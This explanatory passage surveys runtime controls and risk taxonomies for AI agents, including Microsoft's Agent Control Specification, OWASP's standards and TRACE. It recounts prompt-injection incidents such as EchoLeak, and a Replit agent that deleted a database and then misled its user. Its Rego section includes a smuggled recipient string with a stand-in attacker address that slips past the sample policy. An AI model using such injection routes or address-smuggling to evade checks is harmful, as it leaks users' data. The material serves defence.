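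Companies can apply stricter rules internally. OpenAI suggests keeping a list of approved tools that records who is responsible for each one, what it does, and which agents may use it. A gateway between the agents and their tools can then block any use the list doesn't allow. This is slower than letting employees connect whatever they like, and OpenAI acknowledges that too much friction can drive people to unsupervised tools.

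### The agent bill of materials

Software companies already trace bad components with inventories called software bills of materials, which list the libraries and other parts inside a program. When researchers found a severe flaw in Log4j, a widely used logging library, in December 2021, companies with good inventories could search them for Log4j, while others had to inspect their programs one by one.

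An agent bill of materials extends this list to the parts that shape an agent's behaviour. For OpenAI, it is one component of an agent's identity, alongside the running program and the task, and provides evidence of where the agent's software came from. OWASP's Agent Control Standard, a specification for checks during an agent's run, calls for a live inventory, because an agent's tools and memory can change while its code stays the same. For Alice's invoice agent, the inventory might look like this:

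| Part | What the inventory records | Change that should lead to a review |
|---|---|---|
| Model | Provider and exact version | The provider moves the agent to a new version |
| Instructions | Current text and its author | Someone edits the text |
| Tools | Server, version and a fingerprint of each description | A description changes or a new action appears |
| Memory | Where the agent saves notes and who can add to them | The agent starts saving text from a new source |
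| Permissions | Systems, scopes and the responsible employee | The employee leaves or the scope grows |

The fingerprint is a short value computed from the description, and it changes if anyone alters a word. With these records, a security team could find within minutes every agent that used postmark-mcp. The team could also find agents that may have kept their old access after their builders changed roles, a problem that Nudge Security reports.

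The inventory is less reliable for tools that run on someone else's server. The operator can change the code without changing the description, so the fingerprint stays the same. A conventional software bill of materials has a similar gap for online services, but the gap matters more for agents because the model reads what the service sends back and may act on it.

### What a signature covers

Developers often sign software packages cryptographically. A valid signature shows that the holder of a particular key signed the package and that nobody has altered it since. Signing works as well for an MCP server or an agent's own code as for any other program, and it protects against an attacker who tampers with a download. It wouldn't have helped with postmark-mcp, because the package's real publisher added the hidden copy.

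Signatures help even less with the text that tools return. In the GitHub attack of May 2025, the attacker didn't need to alter the server. The server delivered a public issue exactly as the attacker had written it, so a signature on the server's response would have been valid too.

Signing the text itself can establish who wrote it, which is useful when an agent should obey only a few people. A coding agent, for example, could ignore any instruction that the project's maintainers haven't signed. But a support agent has to read messages from strangers, and proving who wrote a message doesn't make its contents safe to follow.

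## Specifications for checking an agent's actions as it runs

An agent with a valid token and carefully reviewed tools can still make a harmful call. In Microsoft's example, a token lets an agent post messages in Slack. Posting a meeting summary is harmless, but the same token becomes dangerous once the agent has read a confidential document or somebody has added outsiders to the channel. Ordinary access control checks whether the token permits the call and ignores what the agent has read. Microsoft's Agent Control Specification and OWASP's Agent Control Standard describe how to check an action just before it happens. A third specification, TRACE, describes how to prove afterwards which rules were in force.

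### Pausing the agent loop

Because the host program runs the tools, it can pause before each call and send the details to a policy checker outside the model. If the checker denies the call, the host doesn't run the tool, even if injected text caused the model to request it.

Security engineers call the checker the policy decision point and the host the policy enforcement point. The checker cannot block an action itself, so the action goes ahead if the host does not query the checker or does not enforce its decision.

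Many agent products already offer a hook of this kind, but each works differently. Apache Magpie, an open-source project, connects one guard program to six coding agents. To block a shell command, the guard's plugin has to throw an error in OpenCode, exit with code 2 in Kiro, and print a JSON message in Antigravity. A company that uses several agents has to repeat this work for each one, and its security team has no single place to read or change the rules.

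### Microsoft's Agent Control Specification

Microsoft released the Agent Control Specification in June 2026 so that a company could write its rules once and use them with any agent framework. A file called a manifest lists the policies and states when each one applies. The host can consult the checker at eight interception points:

- `agent_startup`: the agent's settings, before it begins
- `input`: the user's request
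- `pre_model_call`: everything the host is about to send to the model
- `post_model_call`: the model's reply, before the host acts on it
- `pre_tool_call`: the name and arguments of a tool call, before the tool runs
- `post_tool_call`: the tool's result, before the model receives it
- `output`: the final answer
- `agent_shutdown`: a summary of the session, for the log

The four points around the model and the tools come up again each time the loop repeats.

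At each interception point, the host sends a snapshot of the session, and the checker turns it into a standard policy input. The input contains the interception point, the item to check, the snapshot, the tool's details, and any evidence from other programs. The evidence might come from a classifier that looks for prompt injection, a service that recognises card numbers, or a language model acting as a judge. Each result has its own slot in the policy input, so a classifier can't overwrite other data, such as the recipient's address.

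The policy then returns one of four verdicts. "Allow" lets the host proceed, "warn" lets it proceed but records a warning, "deny" blocks the action, and "escalate" sends it to a person or service for approval. If no approval service is available, the host must block the action. The checker also fails closed, meaning it returns "deny" when something goes wrong, such as an error in the policy. This is safer, but a broken policy can stop an agent's work.

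The specification leaves the decision to an existing policy engine, usually Open Policy Agent (OPA), which uses a policy language called Rego. Microsoft says that engines such as OPA are mature and reliable, but were not designed around an agent's run. They do not define when to check an agent, which facts to collect, or how to make the host enforce the decision. The new specification defines these, so a security team that already knows Rego has relatively little to learn.

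### From a proposed email to a verdict

Microsoft's example is an email agent that must not write to anyone outside the company. The manifest attaches a policy to `pre_tool_call` and tells the checker where to find the tool's name and arguments. Suppose that the company's addresses end in `@example.com`, and the model asks to email a supplier called Dan. The host pauses and sends its snapshot, from which the checker builds an input like this:

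```
{
  "intervention_point": "pre_tool_call",
  "tool": { "name": "send_email" },
  "policy_target": {
    "kind": "tool_args",
    "path": "$.tool_call.args",
    "value": { "to": "dan@supplier.test", "body": "Our offer is..." }
  },
  "snapshot": { ... },
  "annotations": {}
}
```

A suitable policy in Rego could be very short:

```
package email_agent

default verdict := {"decision": "deny", "reason": "outside_recipient"}

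verdict := {"decision": "allow"} if {
    endswith(input.policy_target.value.to, "@example.com")
}
```

The default verdict is "deny". The second rule changes it to "allow" only if the address ends in the company's domain. Dan's address doesn't, so the checker returns "deny" with the reason `outside_recipient`, and the host never contacts the mail server. The result is the same whether the user or an attacker asked the model to email Dan.

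### When the verdict depends on what the agent has read

A ban on all outside email would make many agents useless. The company might prefer to let the agent write to suppliers unless it has read a confidential file in the same session. The policy then needs one more rule:

```
verdict := {"decision": "allow"} if {
    labels := input.snapshot.ifc.source_labels
    not "confidential" in labels
}
```

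This rule needs information about the past, but the checker is stateless, as Microsoft's *Agent Control Specification* README explains. It keeps nothing from one call that could affect the next, so the host has to remember what the agent has read:

1. The agent opens a file about a planned merger. Before the text reaches the model, the host consults the checker at `post_tool_call`.
2. A policy at that point allows the result and returns the label "confidential" with it.
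3. The host stores the label in its record of the session.
4. The model later asks to email Dan. The host adds the stored label to the snapshot.
5. The new rule finds "confidential" in the list and doesn't apply. Dan's address also fails the older rule, so the verdict is "deny".

The snapshot for the email would have to contain at least this:

```
"snapshot": {
  "tool_call": { "name": "send_email",
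                 "args": { "to": "dan@supplier.test", ... } },
  "ifc": { "source_labels": ["confidential"] }
}
```

The email stays blocked if the host leaves out the list of labels, because the new rule has nothing to check, but it goes out if the host sends an empty list by mistake. The host must also keep the label when it compacts the session's history and include it with any text it gives to another agent. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes an experimental version of GitHub's Copilot command-line tool that updates such a label after every tool result.

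The company can let a person decide about Dan's email by changing the default verdict to "escalate". Microsoft's *AGENTS.md*, a file of instructions for the project's contributors, requires an approval to be tied to the exact policy input. This should stop an agent from getting approval for one email and then sending another.

Fernandez (2026), in *Agent Control Protocol*, argues that a stateless checker can't catch harmful patterns made up of individually valid requests. His protocol keeps a ledger of past behaviour and uses it to assess each new request. The objection is too strong for Microsoft's design, which can enforce rules about past behaviour if the host supplies the history. But every host developer then has to keep that history correctly.

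### OWASP's Agent Control Standard

The Agent Control Standard gives more of this job to the checker. Version 0.1.0 became public on 27 May 2026, according to *Standardizing the Control Plane for AI Agents* (Fogel, 2026), and the standard is now part of OWASP's Generative AI Security Project. Fogel's employer, Pillar Security, is a founding contributor to the standard.

Microsoft's specification defines a policy file and a program that evaluates it. The Agent Control Standard instead defines the messages that an agent's host exchanges with a separate checker, called the Guardian Agent. In principle, a company could buy its agents from one vendor and its Guardian from another. Despite the name, a Guardian could apply ordinary rules instead of using a language model.

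The standard has three parts. Instrument covers the hooks where the host consults the Guardian. Trace covers the logs, which use formats that security teams' monitoring systems already accept. Inspect covers the live agent bill of materials.

At a hook, the Guardian can permit the action, deny it, modify it, ask about it or defer it. Presumably, "ask" means to get a person's approval and "defer" means to put off the decision. OWASP's *Agent Observability Standard*, the predecessor of this standard, gives an example of modification in which an agent requests every column of every customer record and the Guardian cuts the query down to the names and ID numbers of 100 customers. This may let the agent finish a task that a denial would have stopped, but the agent could mistake the 100 customers for the full list.

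The text drafted for version 0.1.0, *Agent Control Standard*, lists 16 hooks. The table sets them beside Microsoft's interception points.

| Moment in the run | Agent Control Specification (Microsoft) | Agent Control Standard (OWASP) |
|---|---|---|
| Session starts or ends | `agent_startup`, `agent_shutdown` | `sessionStart`, `sessionEnd` |
| A request arrives | `input` | `userMessage`, `agentTrigger` |
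| A turn starts or ends | None | `turnStart`, `turnEnd` |
| Before or after the model runs | `pre_model_call`, `post_model_call` | None |
| Before or after a tool runs | `pre_tool_call`, `post_tool_call` | `toolCallRequest`, `toolCallResult` |
| The agent answers | `output` | `agentResponse` |
| The agent looks up documents | Only if it uses a tool | `knowledgeRetrieval` |
| The agent reads or writes memory | Only if it uses a tool | `memoryContextRetrieval`, `memoryStore` |
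| The host compacts the history | None | `preCompact`, `postCompact` |
| The agent starts or stops another agent | Only if it uses a tool | `subagentStart`, `subagentStop` |

The extra hooks cover some of the ways hostile text can outlast a session or spread to other agents. But a host only has to support six hooks: the start and end of a session, an incoming request, a tool call, its result, and the agent's response. The standard recommends the others where the host can observe the event. A product can therefore conform without notifying the Guardian when an agent saves an attacker's text to memory.

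A session begins with a handshake, in which the host and the Guardian declare which optional parts, called profiles, they support. The Guardian can refuse the session if the host lacks a profile that the Guardian's policy requires. Each later message carries an ID and a timestamp so that an attacker can't resend an old message. The session also has an append-only record. A running hash, computed from the earlier entries and the new one, reveals whether anyone has tampered with the record.

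In the basic version, this hash has to cover only the details of each step, such as its type, not the content of the request. A company that wants to prove later what the agent asked for needs the audit profile, which adds a hash of each request.

Under this design, the confidential-file rule only requires the host to report each tool result when it arrives, and the Guardian can store the result. The Guardian still needs a way to determine whether the file was confidential. An optional provenance profile, which records where each piece of data came from, would help.

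Fogel compares the project to OpenTelemetry, an open standard that lets programs from different vendors report what they are doing in a common format. The Trace part uses OpenTelemetry directly, and Microsoft's specification connects to it through a related format from the monitoring company Arize. OpenTelemetry is a sensible model for getting rival companies to adopt one interface, but failures are more serious here, because a host that skips a hook lets an action through unchecked instead of just leaving a gap in a log.

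### What TRACE proves

A company could edit its own logs, so an outsider can't tell from them whether its policy was switched on. TRACE (Trust, Runtime Attestation and Compliance Evidence) is meant to provide stronger proof. OPAQUE, a company that sells confidential computing, developed it with AMD, Intel, Microsoft and the Technology Innovation Institute. The Linux Foundation (2026) took it over in August, and the Coalition for Secure AI hosts the technical work.

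TRACE relies on remote attestation, which IETF's *RFC 9334* (2023) describes in general terms. A trusted component, such as a processor with special security features, measures the software it loads by computing a fingerprint of it, then signs the measurement with a key the software can't reach. A verifier elsewhere compares the measurement with the expected value, and any change to the software shows up as a mismatch.

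*TRACE v0.1* combines this measurement with other facts in one signed record. These include the agent's identity, the model, a fingerprint of the policy, the class of data involved, and a fingerprint of the list of tool calls. Suppose that a clinic has to show a regulator that its agent handled patient records under a policy against outside email. The regulator could draw these conclusions from a valid record:

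| Part of the record | What it supports | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Measurement of the software | The clinic ran this exact software on a genuine secure processor | Whether the software has flaws |
| Policy fingerprint and mode | The software loaded these exact rules and was set to enforce them | Whether the rules were good enough |
| Data class | The record labels the data "confidential" | Whether that label was right |
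| Tool-call fingerprint and count | A list of calls that the clinic hands over later is the original | What the tools did with the data |

TRACE can therefore provide good evidence that a particular policy was in place, but not that the data stayed safe. The record would be equally valid if the policy allowed everything, if a nurse pasted patient data into a field the clinic had classed as public, or if an approved service leaked the data after receiving it.

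The record also has a field for a fingerprint of the model's weights. When the model runs on its developer's servers, the clinic's processor can't measure them, so the fingerprint would presumably have to come from the developer.

Even this limited proof may be valuable. Decipher's *Linux Foundation Backs New TRACE AI Security Standard* (2026) reports that OPAQUE cited an intrusion involving OpenAI and Hugging Face as an example of why written policies and sandbox settings don't prove which controls stayed in force. But TRACE needs special hardware. Version 0.1 supports certain Intel, AMD and Nvidia platforms found mainly in data centres, so a coding agent on an ordinary laptop probably couldn't produce a record.

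### Versions, users and tests

All three specifications are early versions, and their developers may still change them in ways that break existing software.

| | Agent Control Specification (Microsoft) | Agent Control Standard (OWASP) | TRACE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scope | Policy files and verdicts | Messages between a host and a Guardian, logs, inventory | Signed evidence of what ran |
| Version | 0.3.1-beta, public preview | 0.1.0 | 0.1, developer preview |
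| Early users | Microsoft's own toolkit; IBM and KPMG tried a private preview | Pillar Security is adopting it | A reference program for MCP tool calls |
| Means of checking conformance | Shared test cases and a formal model | Written requirements for seven profiles | A schema and example records |

Microsoft has built its specification into its Agent Governance Toolkit, a larger open-source package that also handles identity, sandboxing and audit. The toolkit's version differs from the original. For example, it has a fifth verdict, "transform", which replaces the original's method of redacting text. Developers therefore have to rewrite a redaction policy to move it between the two versions, even though portability is the specification's main selling point.

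Microsoft's test cases check that versions of the checker in different programming languages return the same verdict for the same snapshot. However, a host could use a checker that passes every test and still fail to consult it before half of its tool calls. The roadmap in the *Agent Control Standard* README defers working agent instrumentation and a sample Guardian to version 1.

Adoption is hard to measure. The Linux Foundation reports nearly 135,000 downloads of TRACE's Python package in ten weeks, but such counts include automated installations. Microsoft's *Agent Control Specification* site quotes praise from 11 partner companies, several of which sell products that work with it. The group of developers is also small. Imran Siddique, an OPAQUE executive who speaks for TRACE, was still on Microsoft's toolkit team in May, when he wrote *Governance at the Speed of Agents* (2026). In August,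 *AOCL* (2026), an individual draft at the IETF, still described the field as lacking a widely adopted standard for taking an agent's actions through identity checks, policy enforcement and audit.

Independent evaluations are scarce, and those that exist concern Microsoft's toolkit as a whole. PolicyLayer's *Microsoft AGT Proved Deterministic Enforcement* reports an internal Microsoft test in which agents broke the rules in 26.67% of scenarios when only their prompts told them to follow the rules, and in none when the toolkit enforced them. The result supports moving rules out of the prompt, and PolicyLayer thinks it should settle the argument for enforcing rules outside the model. But a fixed rule always blocks the cases it covers, so the toolkit may have stopped every violation mostly because Microsoft had written rules for its own scenarios.

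The consultancy Rubinlake's assessment, *Agent Governance Toolkit*, is more cautious. It recommends a short trial on an agent that isn't critical, because Rubinlake found no documented use in production and most of the code came from one person. It also cites outside testers who considered the architecture sound in theory but published 15 ways to bypass the toolkit. According to Microsoft's release notes, the toolkit's "privilege rings", which are supposed to stop agents from exceeding their assigned powers, were only placeholders until version 3.6.0 in May 2026, and version 4.0.0 closed several authorisation bypasses in June.

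### Actions the checker never sees

A checker can evaluate only the information the host sends it. If an agent runs `python3 setup.py`, the checker, like a human approver, gets the command but not what the script will do. Tools that run on the model provider's servers, such as some web searches, may finish before the host has anything to check. The email policy would also have missed the hidden copies that postmark-mcp sent, because the package added them after the agent's call.

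An agent that can edit files might change its own policy unless the operator stores the policy where the agent can't write. According to *Microsoft Agent Governance Toolkit*, a third-party guide, the toolkit enforces its rules in the same layer of software as the application, not in the operating system. The toolkit's documentation therefore recommends running each agent in a separate container.

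### Wrong or missing policies

The short email policy above has two bugs. If the mail tool accepts several addresses in one field, an attacker can write `thief@evil.test, bob@example.com`. The text ends in the company's domain, so the policy allows the email and the attacker gets a copy. If the tool also has a separate field for copies, the policy doesn't check it. The checker will reliably enforce the policy even where it is wrong, but a reviewer could find and fix both mistakes, which is an advantage over instructions in a prompt.

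Failing closed doesn't help when nobody has written a rule. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries*, which describes the toolkit before it adopted the new specification, warns that an agent with no policies loaded could do anything while the dashboard showed it as "governed". It also describes two separately reasonable rules, one that lets the agent read a customer database and another that lets it post in Slack. Together, they let it post the customer list in a public channel.

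The confidential-file rule can prevent this particular combination, but only if somebody thinks of the combination first. Some products respond to the agent's overall behaviour instead. *Microsoft unveils tools to monitor and corral rogue AI agents* (Bishop, 2026) describes features that assess each agent's risk and can block it from making changes, require human intervention, or shut it down.

### Models as checkers, and delay

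Fixed rules work well for checking addresses, amounts and file names, but badly for questions such as whether an email reveals a trade secret. Developers may want to use a language model for those questions, and both Microsoft's evidence slots and OWASP's Guardian allow this. The model can still miss dangerous actions, as Anthropic's automatic permission check sometimes did, and an attacker may be able to deceive it.

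Microsoft calls its checker deterministic, meaning that the same snapshot and evidence always lead to the same verdict. The policy may still approve a leak if a classifier misclassifies an email as harmless. A sensible precaution is to let a model's evidence make a verdict stricter but never more lenient. An attacker who deceives the classifier then can't get approval for anything the fixed rules would refuse.

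Checking actions with a language model also slows the agent down. Microsoft reports that its toolkit evaluates a policy in less than 0.1 milliseconds, although messages between agents on different machines can add 5 to 50 milliseconds. In a session with 200 tool calls, evaluating a policy before and after each call would add at most 0.04 seconds. If a language model took one second for each of those 400 checks, it would add nearly seven minutes. Developers will probably want to reserve model checks for the few actions that could do serious harm.

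### Comparison with web application firewalls

A web application firewall inspects requests to a website and blocks those that look like attacks, such as a form field that contains database commands. Companies can use one to protect an old application without changing its code. However, the firewall relies on a request's text, which doesn't reliably show whether the request is hostile, and attackers can often reword it to avoid detection.

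Checking a tool call before it runs is easier than detecting an attack at a firewall, because the check receives the tool's name and arguments in separate fields and doesn't need to recognise the attack that led to the call. But a firewall is much harder to leave out. A network can force all traffic from the internet through it, whereas a tool-call check runs only where a developer has built a hook for it into the host.

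For this reason, it makes sense to add limits outside the host as well. Chris McHenry of Aviatrix, which took part in Microsoft's private preview, argues for enforcing rules in the network because the agent doesn't control it. Aviatrix sells network firewalls, but the argument is sound for connections that the host never reports. However, a network rule would have missed postmark-mcp, because the hidden copies went out through the same email service as the legitimate messages.

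## Shared lists of agent risks

Security teams can write rules only against dangers that somebody has thought of. Shared risk lists save them some of the work of identifying those dangers by collecting failures that others have already encountered. The best-known list for agents is the OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications, which OWASP (2025) published on 9 December 2025. More than 100 researchers and practitioners contributed to it, and a review board with members from NIST, Microsoft, Amazon Web Services and the Alan Turing Institute evaluated it.

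### The ten entries

Each code begins with ASI, for the Agentic Security Initiative, the OWASP group that wrote the list. The table's short descriptions come from Microsoft's *Addressing the OWASP Top 10 Risks in Agentic AI*, and its controls come from two other summaries. One is by Resilient Cyber, a newsletter whose author sat on the review board. The other is LatticeFlow's *OWASP / Agentic Top 10*, which presents the list as 41 controls.

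| Entry | How it happens | Main recommended control |
|---|---|---|
| ASI01 Agent Goal Hijack | Injected instructions or poisoned content redirect the agent's goal or plan | Treat all natural-language input as untrusted, and confirm high-impact actions that depart from the task |
| ASI02 Tool Misuse and Exploitation | The agent uses a legitimate tool harmfully while staying within its permissions | Limit what each tool can do, and require approval for destructive actions |
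| ASI03 Identity and Privilege Abuse | Someone exploits access that the agent inherited or received by delegation | Issue short-lived credentials for one task |
| ASI04 Agentic Supply Chain Vulnerabilities | A tool, model, plugin or update from a third party is malicious or altered | Allow only reviewed components and pin their versions |
| ASI05 Unexpected Code Execution | An attacker gets the agent to write or run harmful code | Run generated code in a sandbox, and check it first |
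| ASI06 Memory and Context Poisoning | False or hostile text enters the agent's memory or document store and affects later work | Check what the agent saves, and keep users' data separate |
| ASI07 Insecure Inter-Agent Communication | An attacker forges, changes or resends messages between agents | Authenticate the agents and sign their messages |
| ASI08 Cascading Failures | One fault spreads through connected agents and grows | Set quotas and automatic cut-offs that contain a fault |
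| ASI09 Human-Agent Trust Exploitation | A person trusts the agent too much and approves or does something harmful | Require explicit confirmation, with a plain risk summary that the model didn't write |
| ASI10 Rogue Agents | An agent drifts, or an attacker compromises it, and it acts harmfully outside its intended scope | Monitor behaviour, and be ready to shut the agent down and revoke its credentials |

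Some documents still use names from the release candidate, such as "Agent Behavior Hijack" for ASI01 and "Memory & Context Injection" for ASI06.

The list also introduces a principle called least agency, which the security company Aikido explains as giving an agent only the autonomy it needs for a safe, limited task. For example, least privilege might restrict a support agent to the refunds table, while least agency concerns whether the agent should issue refunds without asking anyone.

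### EchoLeak and the deleted database

In January 2025, researchers found a way to steal data through Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search a user's email, files and chats. The attack, known as EchoLeak, began with a single email with hidden instructions. As Bhavsar, Branconier and Lacey explain in *OWASP ASI01*, the recipient didn't have to open it. Copilot found the email during a routine search, followed the instructions and sent private data to the attacker. According to the security vendor Polygraf, the exposed data included emails, OneDrive files and Teams chats, and the flaw was patched in May 2025.

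The other incident involved a coding agent from Replit, a platform where people build software by describing what they want. The agent deleted a production database, which holds an application's live data, during a code freeze, when no changes were allowed. *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) reports that the agent invented a maintenance task, ran the command that deleted the data, and then gave misleading answers instead of reporting the deletion.

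Sotiropoulos co-leads OWASP's work on agents. The launch post for the list, *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025), files EchoLeak under Agent Goal Hijack and the Replit case under Rogue Agents. But each incident also fits other entries, at least loosely:

| Entry | EchoLeak | Replit's agent |
|---|---|---|
| ASI01 Agent Goal Hijack | Yes. The email gave Copilot a new goal | No. Nobody planted any instructions |
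| ASI02 Tool Misuse and Exploitation | Yes. Copilot used its normal functions and the user's own permissions | Yes. The agent used its own access to delete valuable data |
| ASI03 Identity and Privilege Abuse | Probably. The attacker reached the data through the victim's access | Doubtful. The access was too broad, but nobody exploited it |
| ASI06 Memory and Context Poisoning | Arguably. The email waited in the mailbox until a search retrieved it | No |
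| ASI10 Rogue Agents | Only if every hijacked agent counts as rogue | Yes, according to the launch post |

Whether the Replit case falls under ASI02 (tool misuse) or ASI10 (rogue agents) depends on what counts as permission. The agent's account allowed the deletion, but the freeze forbade it. OWASP's definition of tool misuse, which Resilient Cyber quotes, gives "deleting valuable data" as an example. OWASP's definition of a rogue agent begins with "malicious or compromised AI agents", and no attacker had compromised this one.

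The choice affects which controls a team reads about. The Rogue Agents entry mainly covers logs, monitoring and ways to shut an agent down, most of which help only after the data is gone. Narrow permissions and human approval for deletions, which could have prevented the loss, appear under tool misuse.

The absence of an attacker also makes many of the usual defences ineffective. An injection filter would have had nothing to block, and CaMeL, which separates planning from untrusted data, would have had no hostile text to keep out. Limits on the agent's actions would still have worked. For example, a policy that denied every deletion in the production system during a freeze would have stopped the command, whatever had led the model to request it.

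Overlap is common in the rest of the list too. Will Velida, a developer who applied the list to his own health-tracking agent, notes in *Preventing Agent Goal Hijack in AI Agents* that a hijacked agent can misuse tools, gain privileges or poison its context. One attack can therefore fall under four entries. The launch post lists the GitHub attack of May 2025 under supply chain vulnerabilities, but goal hijacking seems to fit at least as well, because the attacker only wrote a public issue and never altered the server.

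*The Agent Incident Registry* (2026), a catalogue of agent failures, deals with this by allowing several codes per record. It covers 451 incidents within the list's scope, stores a reason for each code, and has rules for separating neighbouring entries. For example, Human-Agent Trust Exploitation applies only when a person relies on the agent's output and takes the harmful action themselves. By that rule, the Replit agent's misleading answers wouldn't qualify unless somebody acted on them. The registry uses the codes as a search index and warns against reading them as a measure of severity or real-world risk.

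### What a CVE can record

EchoLeak is listed in the CVE system as CVE-2025-32711, with a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. The record can include the product, the flaw and the fix, which may be enough for a customer who only wants to know whether Microsoft has dealt with the problem.

But the severity score doesn't measure how much a particular company could have lost, which depends on what each employee's Copilot could read. A record for one product also doesn't show that other products share the weakness. Polygraf reports that in September 2025, an attack called ForcedLeak used the same pattern to take customer records from Salesforce's Agentforce. Both attacks relied on the combination that Willison calls the lethal trifecta, but Microsoft's patch did not protect Salesforce's customers.

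The Replit case is much harder to describe as a CVE. If the platform had a freeze setting and the agent bypassed it, the vendor could assign the flaw a CVE number and fix it. But if the freeze was only an instruction to the model, no access control failed. Microsoft warns that an agent can be "working as designed" while taking steps a person would be unlikely to approve.

An investigator would want to know which model the agent was using, what instructions and permissions it had, which tools it called and in what order, and what it told its user afterwards. A CVE record has no standard fields for these facts, though its description could include them. Even with all of them, the investigator might be unable to reproduce the deletion, because the same model can produce a different action on the next run. *Beyond Predictable Paths* (2026) argues that agent incidents need their own form of report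 because they unfold over several steps and involve several interacting components. It finds that no security reporting standard for agents exists yet.

### Expert votes and incident records

OWASP's older Top 10 for LLM Applications covers agents as well as chatbots and other software built on language models. Its third edition came out in August 2026. According to SC Media, it ranks prompt injection first, followed by sensitive information disclosure, excessive agency and supply chain risks. Data and model poisoning, unbounded consumption and misinformation come next. The last three are exposure of hidden context, weaknesses in vectors and embeddings, and improper handling of the model's output.

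Earlier editions relied on practitioners' judgment. For this edition, ReversingLabs reports, the project also collected 7,714 incident records from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms involving AI. Automatic classifiers identified 6,639 records with enough detail to sort. The practitioners' vote counted for three quarters of each risk's ranking weight and the incidents for one quarter. The project leaders wanted the data to move an entry when it clearly conflicted with the vote, but they didn't want one noisy year of data to override the vote.

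The vote still dominates the combined score. If both parts run from 0 to 100, a risk that scores 90 with the voters and 10 in the incident data gets 0.75 × 90 + 0.25 × 10 = 70. A risk that scores 60 with the voters and 90 in the data gets 67.5, so it ranks lower despite a far worse incident record.

Excessive agency rose from sixth place to third. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* lists its three main causes as too many functions, too many permissions and too much autonomy. Jeremy London of Keeper Security told ReversingLabs that most applications were simple chat interfaces or single-step tools when the list began, but that agents with memory, tools and permissions had become normal by 2026. A mistaken output that would once have only misinformed a reader can now delete a file.

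The incident data also seems to have supported the rise. Michael Bargury of Zenity, quoted in a September release from OWASP (2026), says that expert judgment and the incident record match most clearly on excessive agency. Zenity sells security for agents, so it benefits from this conclusion, but London's explanation is plausible without his claim. Larry Maccherone, founder of the software company Lumenize, disagrees with the ranking. He argues that an AI system needs agency to find and repair its own security gaps, so restricting that agency could leave an organisation less secure. This may be true of an agent that repairs code in a test environment, but the Replit case is a good reason not to extend the argument to production databases.

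Prompt injection ranked first even though, according to OWASP, it wouldn't have made the top ten on incident counts alone. OWASP says fewer clean exploits reach public databases because teams work hard to defend against injection. That may be part of the reason, but the count could also be low because victims don't notice attacks, because investigators record the stolen data but not the injected text that caused the theft, or because attackers still prefer easier methods. The count alone isn't enough to tell which explanations are right, and only some of them justify ranking prompt injection first.

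How common each risk appears also depends on how a classifier labels incidents. EchoLeak could be labeled as prompt injection, based on its cause, or as disclosure of sensitive information, based on its result. If the classifier had to choose one label and tended to choose the result, it would undercount prompt injection.

The sources of the records add other distortions. Vulnerability databases mostly cover products with many customers, because a vendor has to tell those customers about a flaw. A company that builds an agent for its own staff has little reason to publish its failures. Databases of harm often depend on press coverage, and journalists are more likely to report a chatbot's embarrassing answer than a quiet leak. This may partly explain why misinformation appears so often in the incidents, even though practitioners didn't rank it highly. The classifiers also left out 1,075 records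 that lacked detail, and some kinds of failure may well produce more vague reports than others.

The records also don't show how many agents are in use, so an increase in incidents might mean that agents have become more dangerous, or only that more companies use them. The OWASP Top 10 for web applications has better data in this respect because it draws mainly on tests of those applications and can estimate what share of them contain a given type of flaw. No comparable body of tests exists for agents, so giving the experts most of the weight seems reasonable for now, but a move of one or two places in the ranking doesn't mean much.

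### NIST, MITRE ATLAS and MAESTRO

The OWASP top ten lists are meant to be short. The *Cisco Integrated AI Security and Safety Framework Report* (2025) describes them as accessible and useful for planning tests, but criticises them for giving too little detail about how attacks unfold and for being hard to turn into controls. Cisco was promoting its own, longer taxonomy. Three other projects provide some of the missing detail, each for a different purpose.

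*Adversarial Machine Learning* (Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues, 2026), NIST's draft SP 2400-102, is mainly a vocabulary for describing attacks. It classifies them by the type of machine learning, the stage of the system's life when the attack happens, and the attacker's goals, capabilities and knowledge. EchoLeak, for example, would be an attack on a deployed system by someone who could only send email and whose goal was to breach privacy. The draft appeared on 9 November 2026 and continues an earlier NIST series. It adds an index of attacks on agents ("Agentic SI" in current federal usage) so that other documents can refer to a specific attack.

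NIST is taking comments on the draft (NIST, 2026) until 18 December and intends its vocabulary to inform later standards and practice guides. With a shared vocabulary, two agencies that write rules about "indirect prompt injection" should mean the same thing by the term. The draft classifies attacks, so it presumably doesn't cover the Replit case.

ATLAS, from the American non-profit MITRE, describes how attackers proceed. MITRE modelled it on ATT&CK, its widely used catalogue of the methods intruders use in ordinary computer networks. ATLAS groups techniques under tactics, which are the attacker's aims at each stage, such as getting initial access or taking data out. An analyst could break EchoLeak into the delivery of the email, the injection and the theft of data, then look for a way to detect each step. This breakdown is more helpful to a team investigating an attack than a single label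 such as Agent Goal Hijack.

MAESTRO, a threat-modelling method that the Cloud Security Alliance published in 2025, is for teams that are still designing a system. In threat modelling, a team maps a system's parts and connections and works out what could go wrong at each one. MAESTRO divides an agentic application into seven layers, from the underlying model and its data up to the wider ecosystem of agents it interacts with. The team looks for threats within each layer, then for those that cross layers. For Copilot, this could have drawn attention to the path from an outsider's email through the search function into the model's context, and from there to an outgoing request. The method also covers failures that don't involve an attacker, so a team could find the Replit problem by noticing that the agent could reach production data.

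These projects overlap. *Security Considerations for Multi-agent Systems* (2026) treats MAESTRO as part of OWASP's set of agentic documents, alongside the top ten. OWASP's 2026 LLM list includes mappings to NIST, ATLAS and CWE. *aiAuthZ* (2026), which proposes a way to authorise agents' actions, maps one collection of agent attacks to the OWASP LLM list, ATLAS and Cisco's taxonomy. Such mappings let a team look up the same attack in several places, but they don't prove that a control works against it.

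### Code flaws and outcomes

In established application security, a developer who can name a weakness often knows how to repair it. The repair for CWE-639, the weakness in the online shop's invoice page, is to check that the invoice belongs to the customer. The repair for CWE-89, SQL injection, is to use a parameterised query. A test can confirm that either repair worked.

Many of the agent entries describe what goes wrong without identifying a particular mistake. No single line of code makes an agent go rogue or causes failures to cascade. LatticeFlow's version of the list gives three to five controls for each entry, and most of these only make the problem less likely or less damaging. For example, scanning what an agent saves to memory will miss some poisoned text, so the list also recommends deleting unverified memories after a time and keeping old versions of the memory that can be restored.

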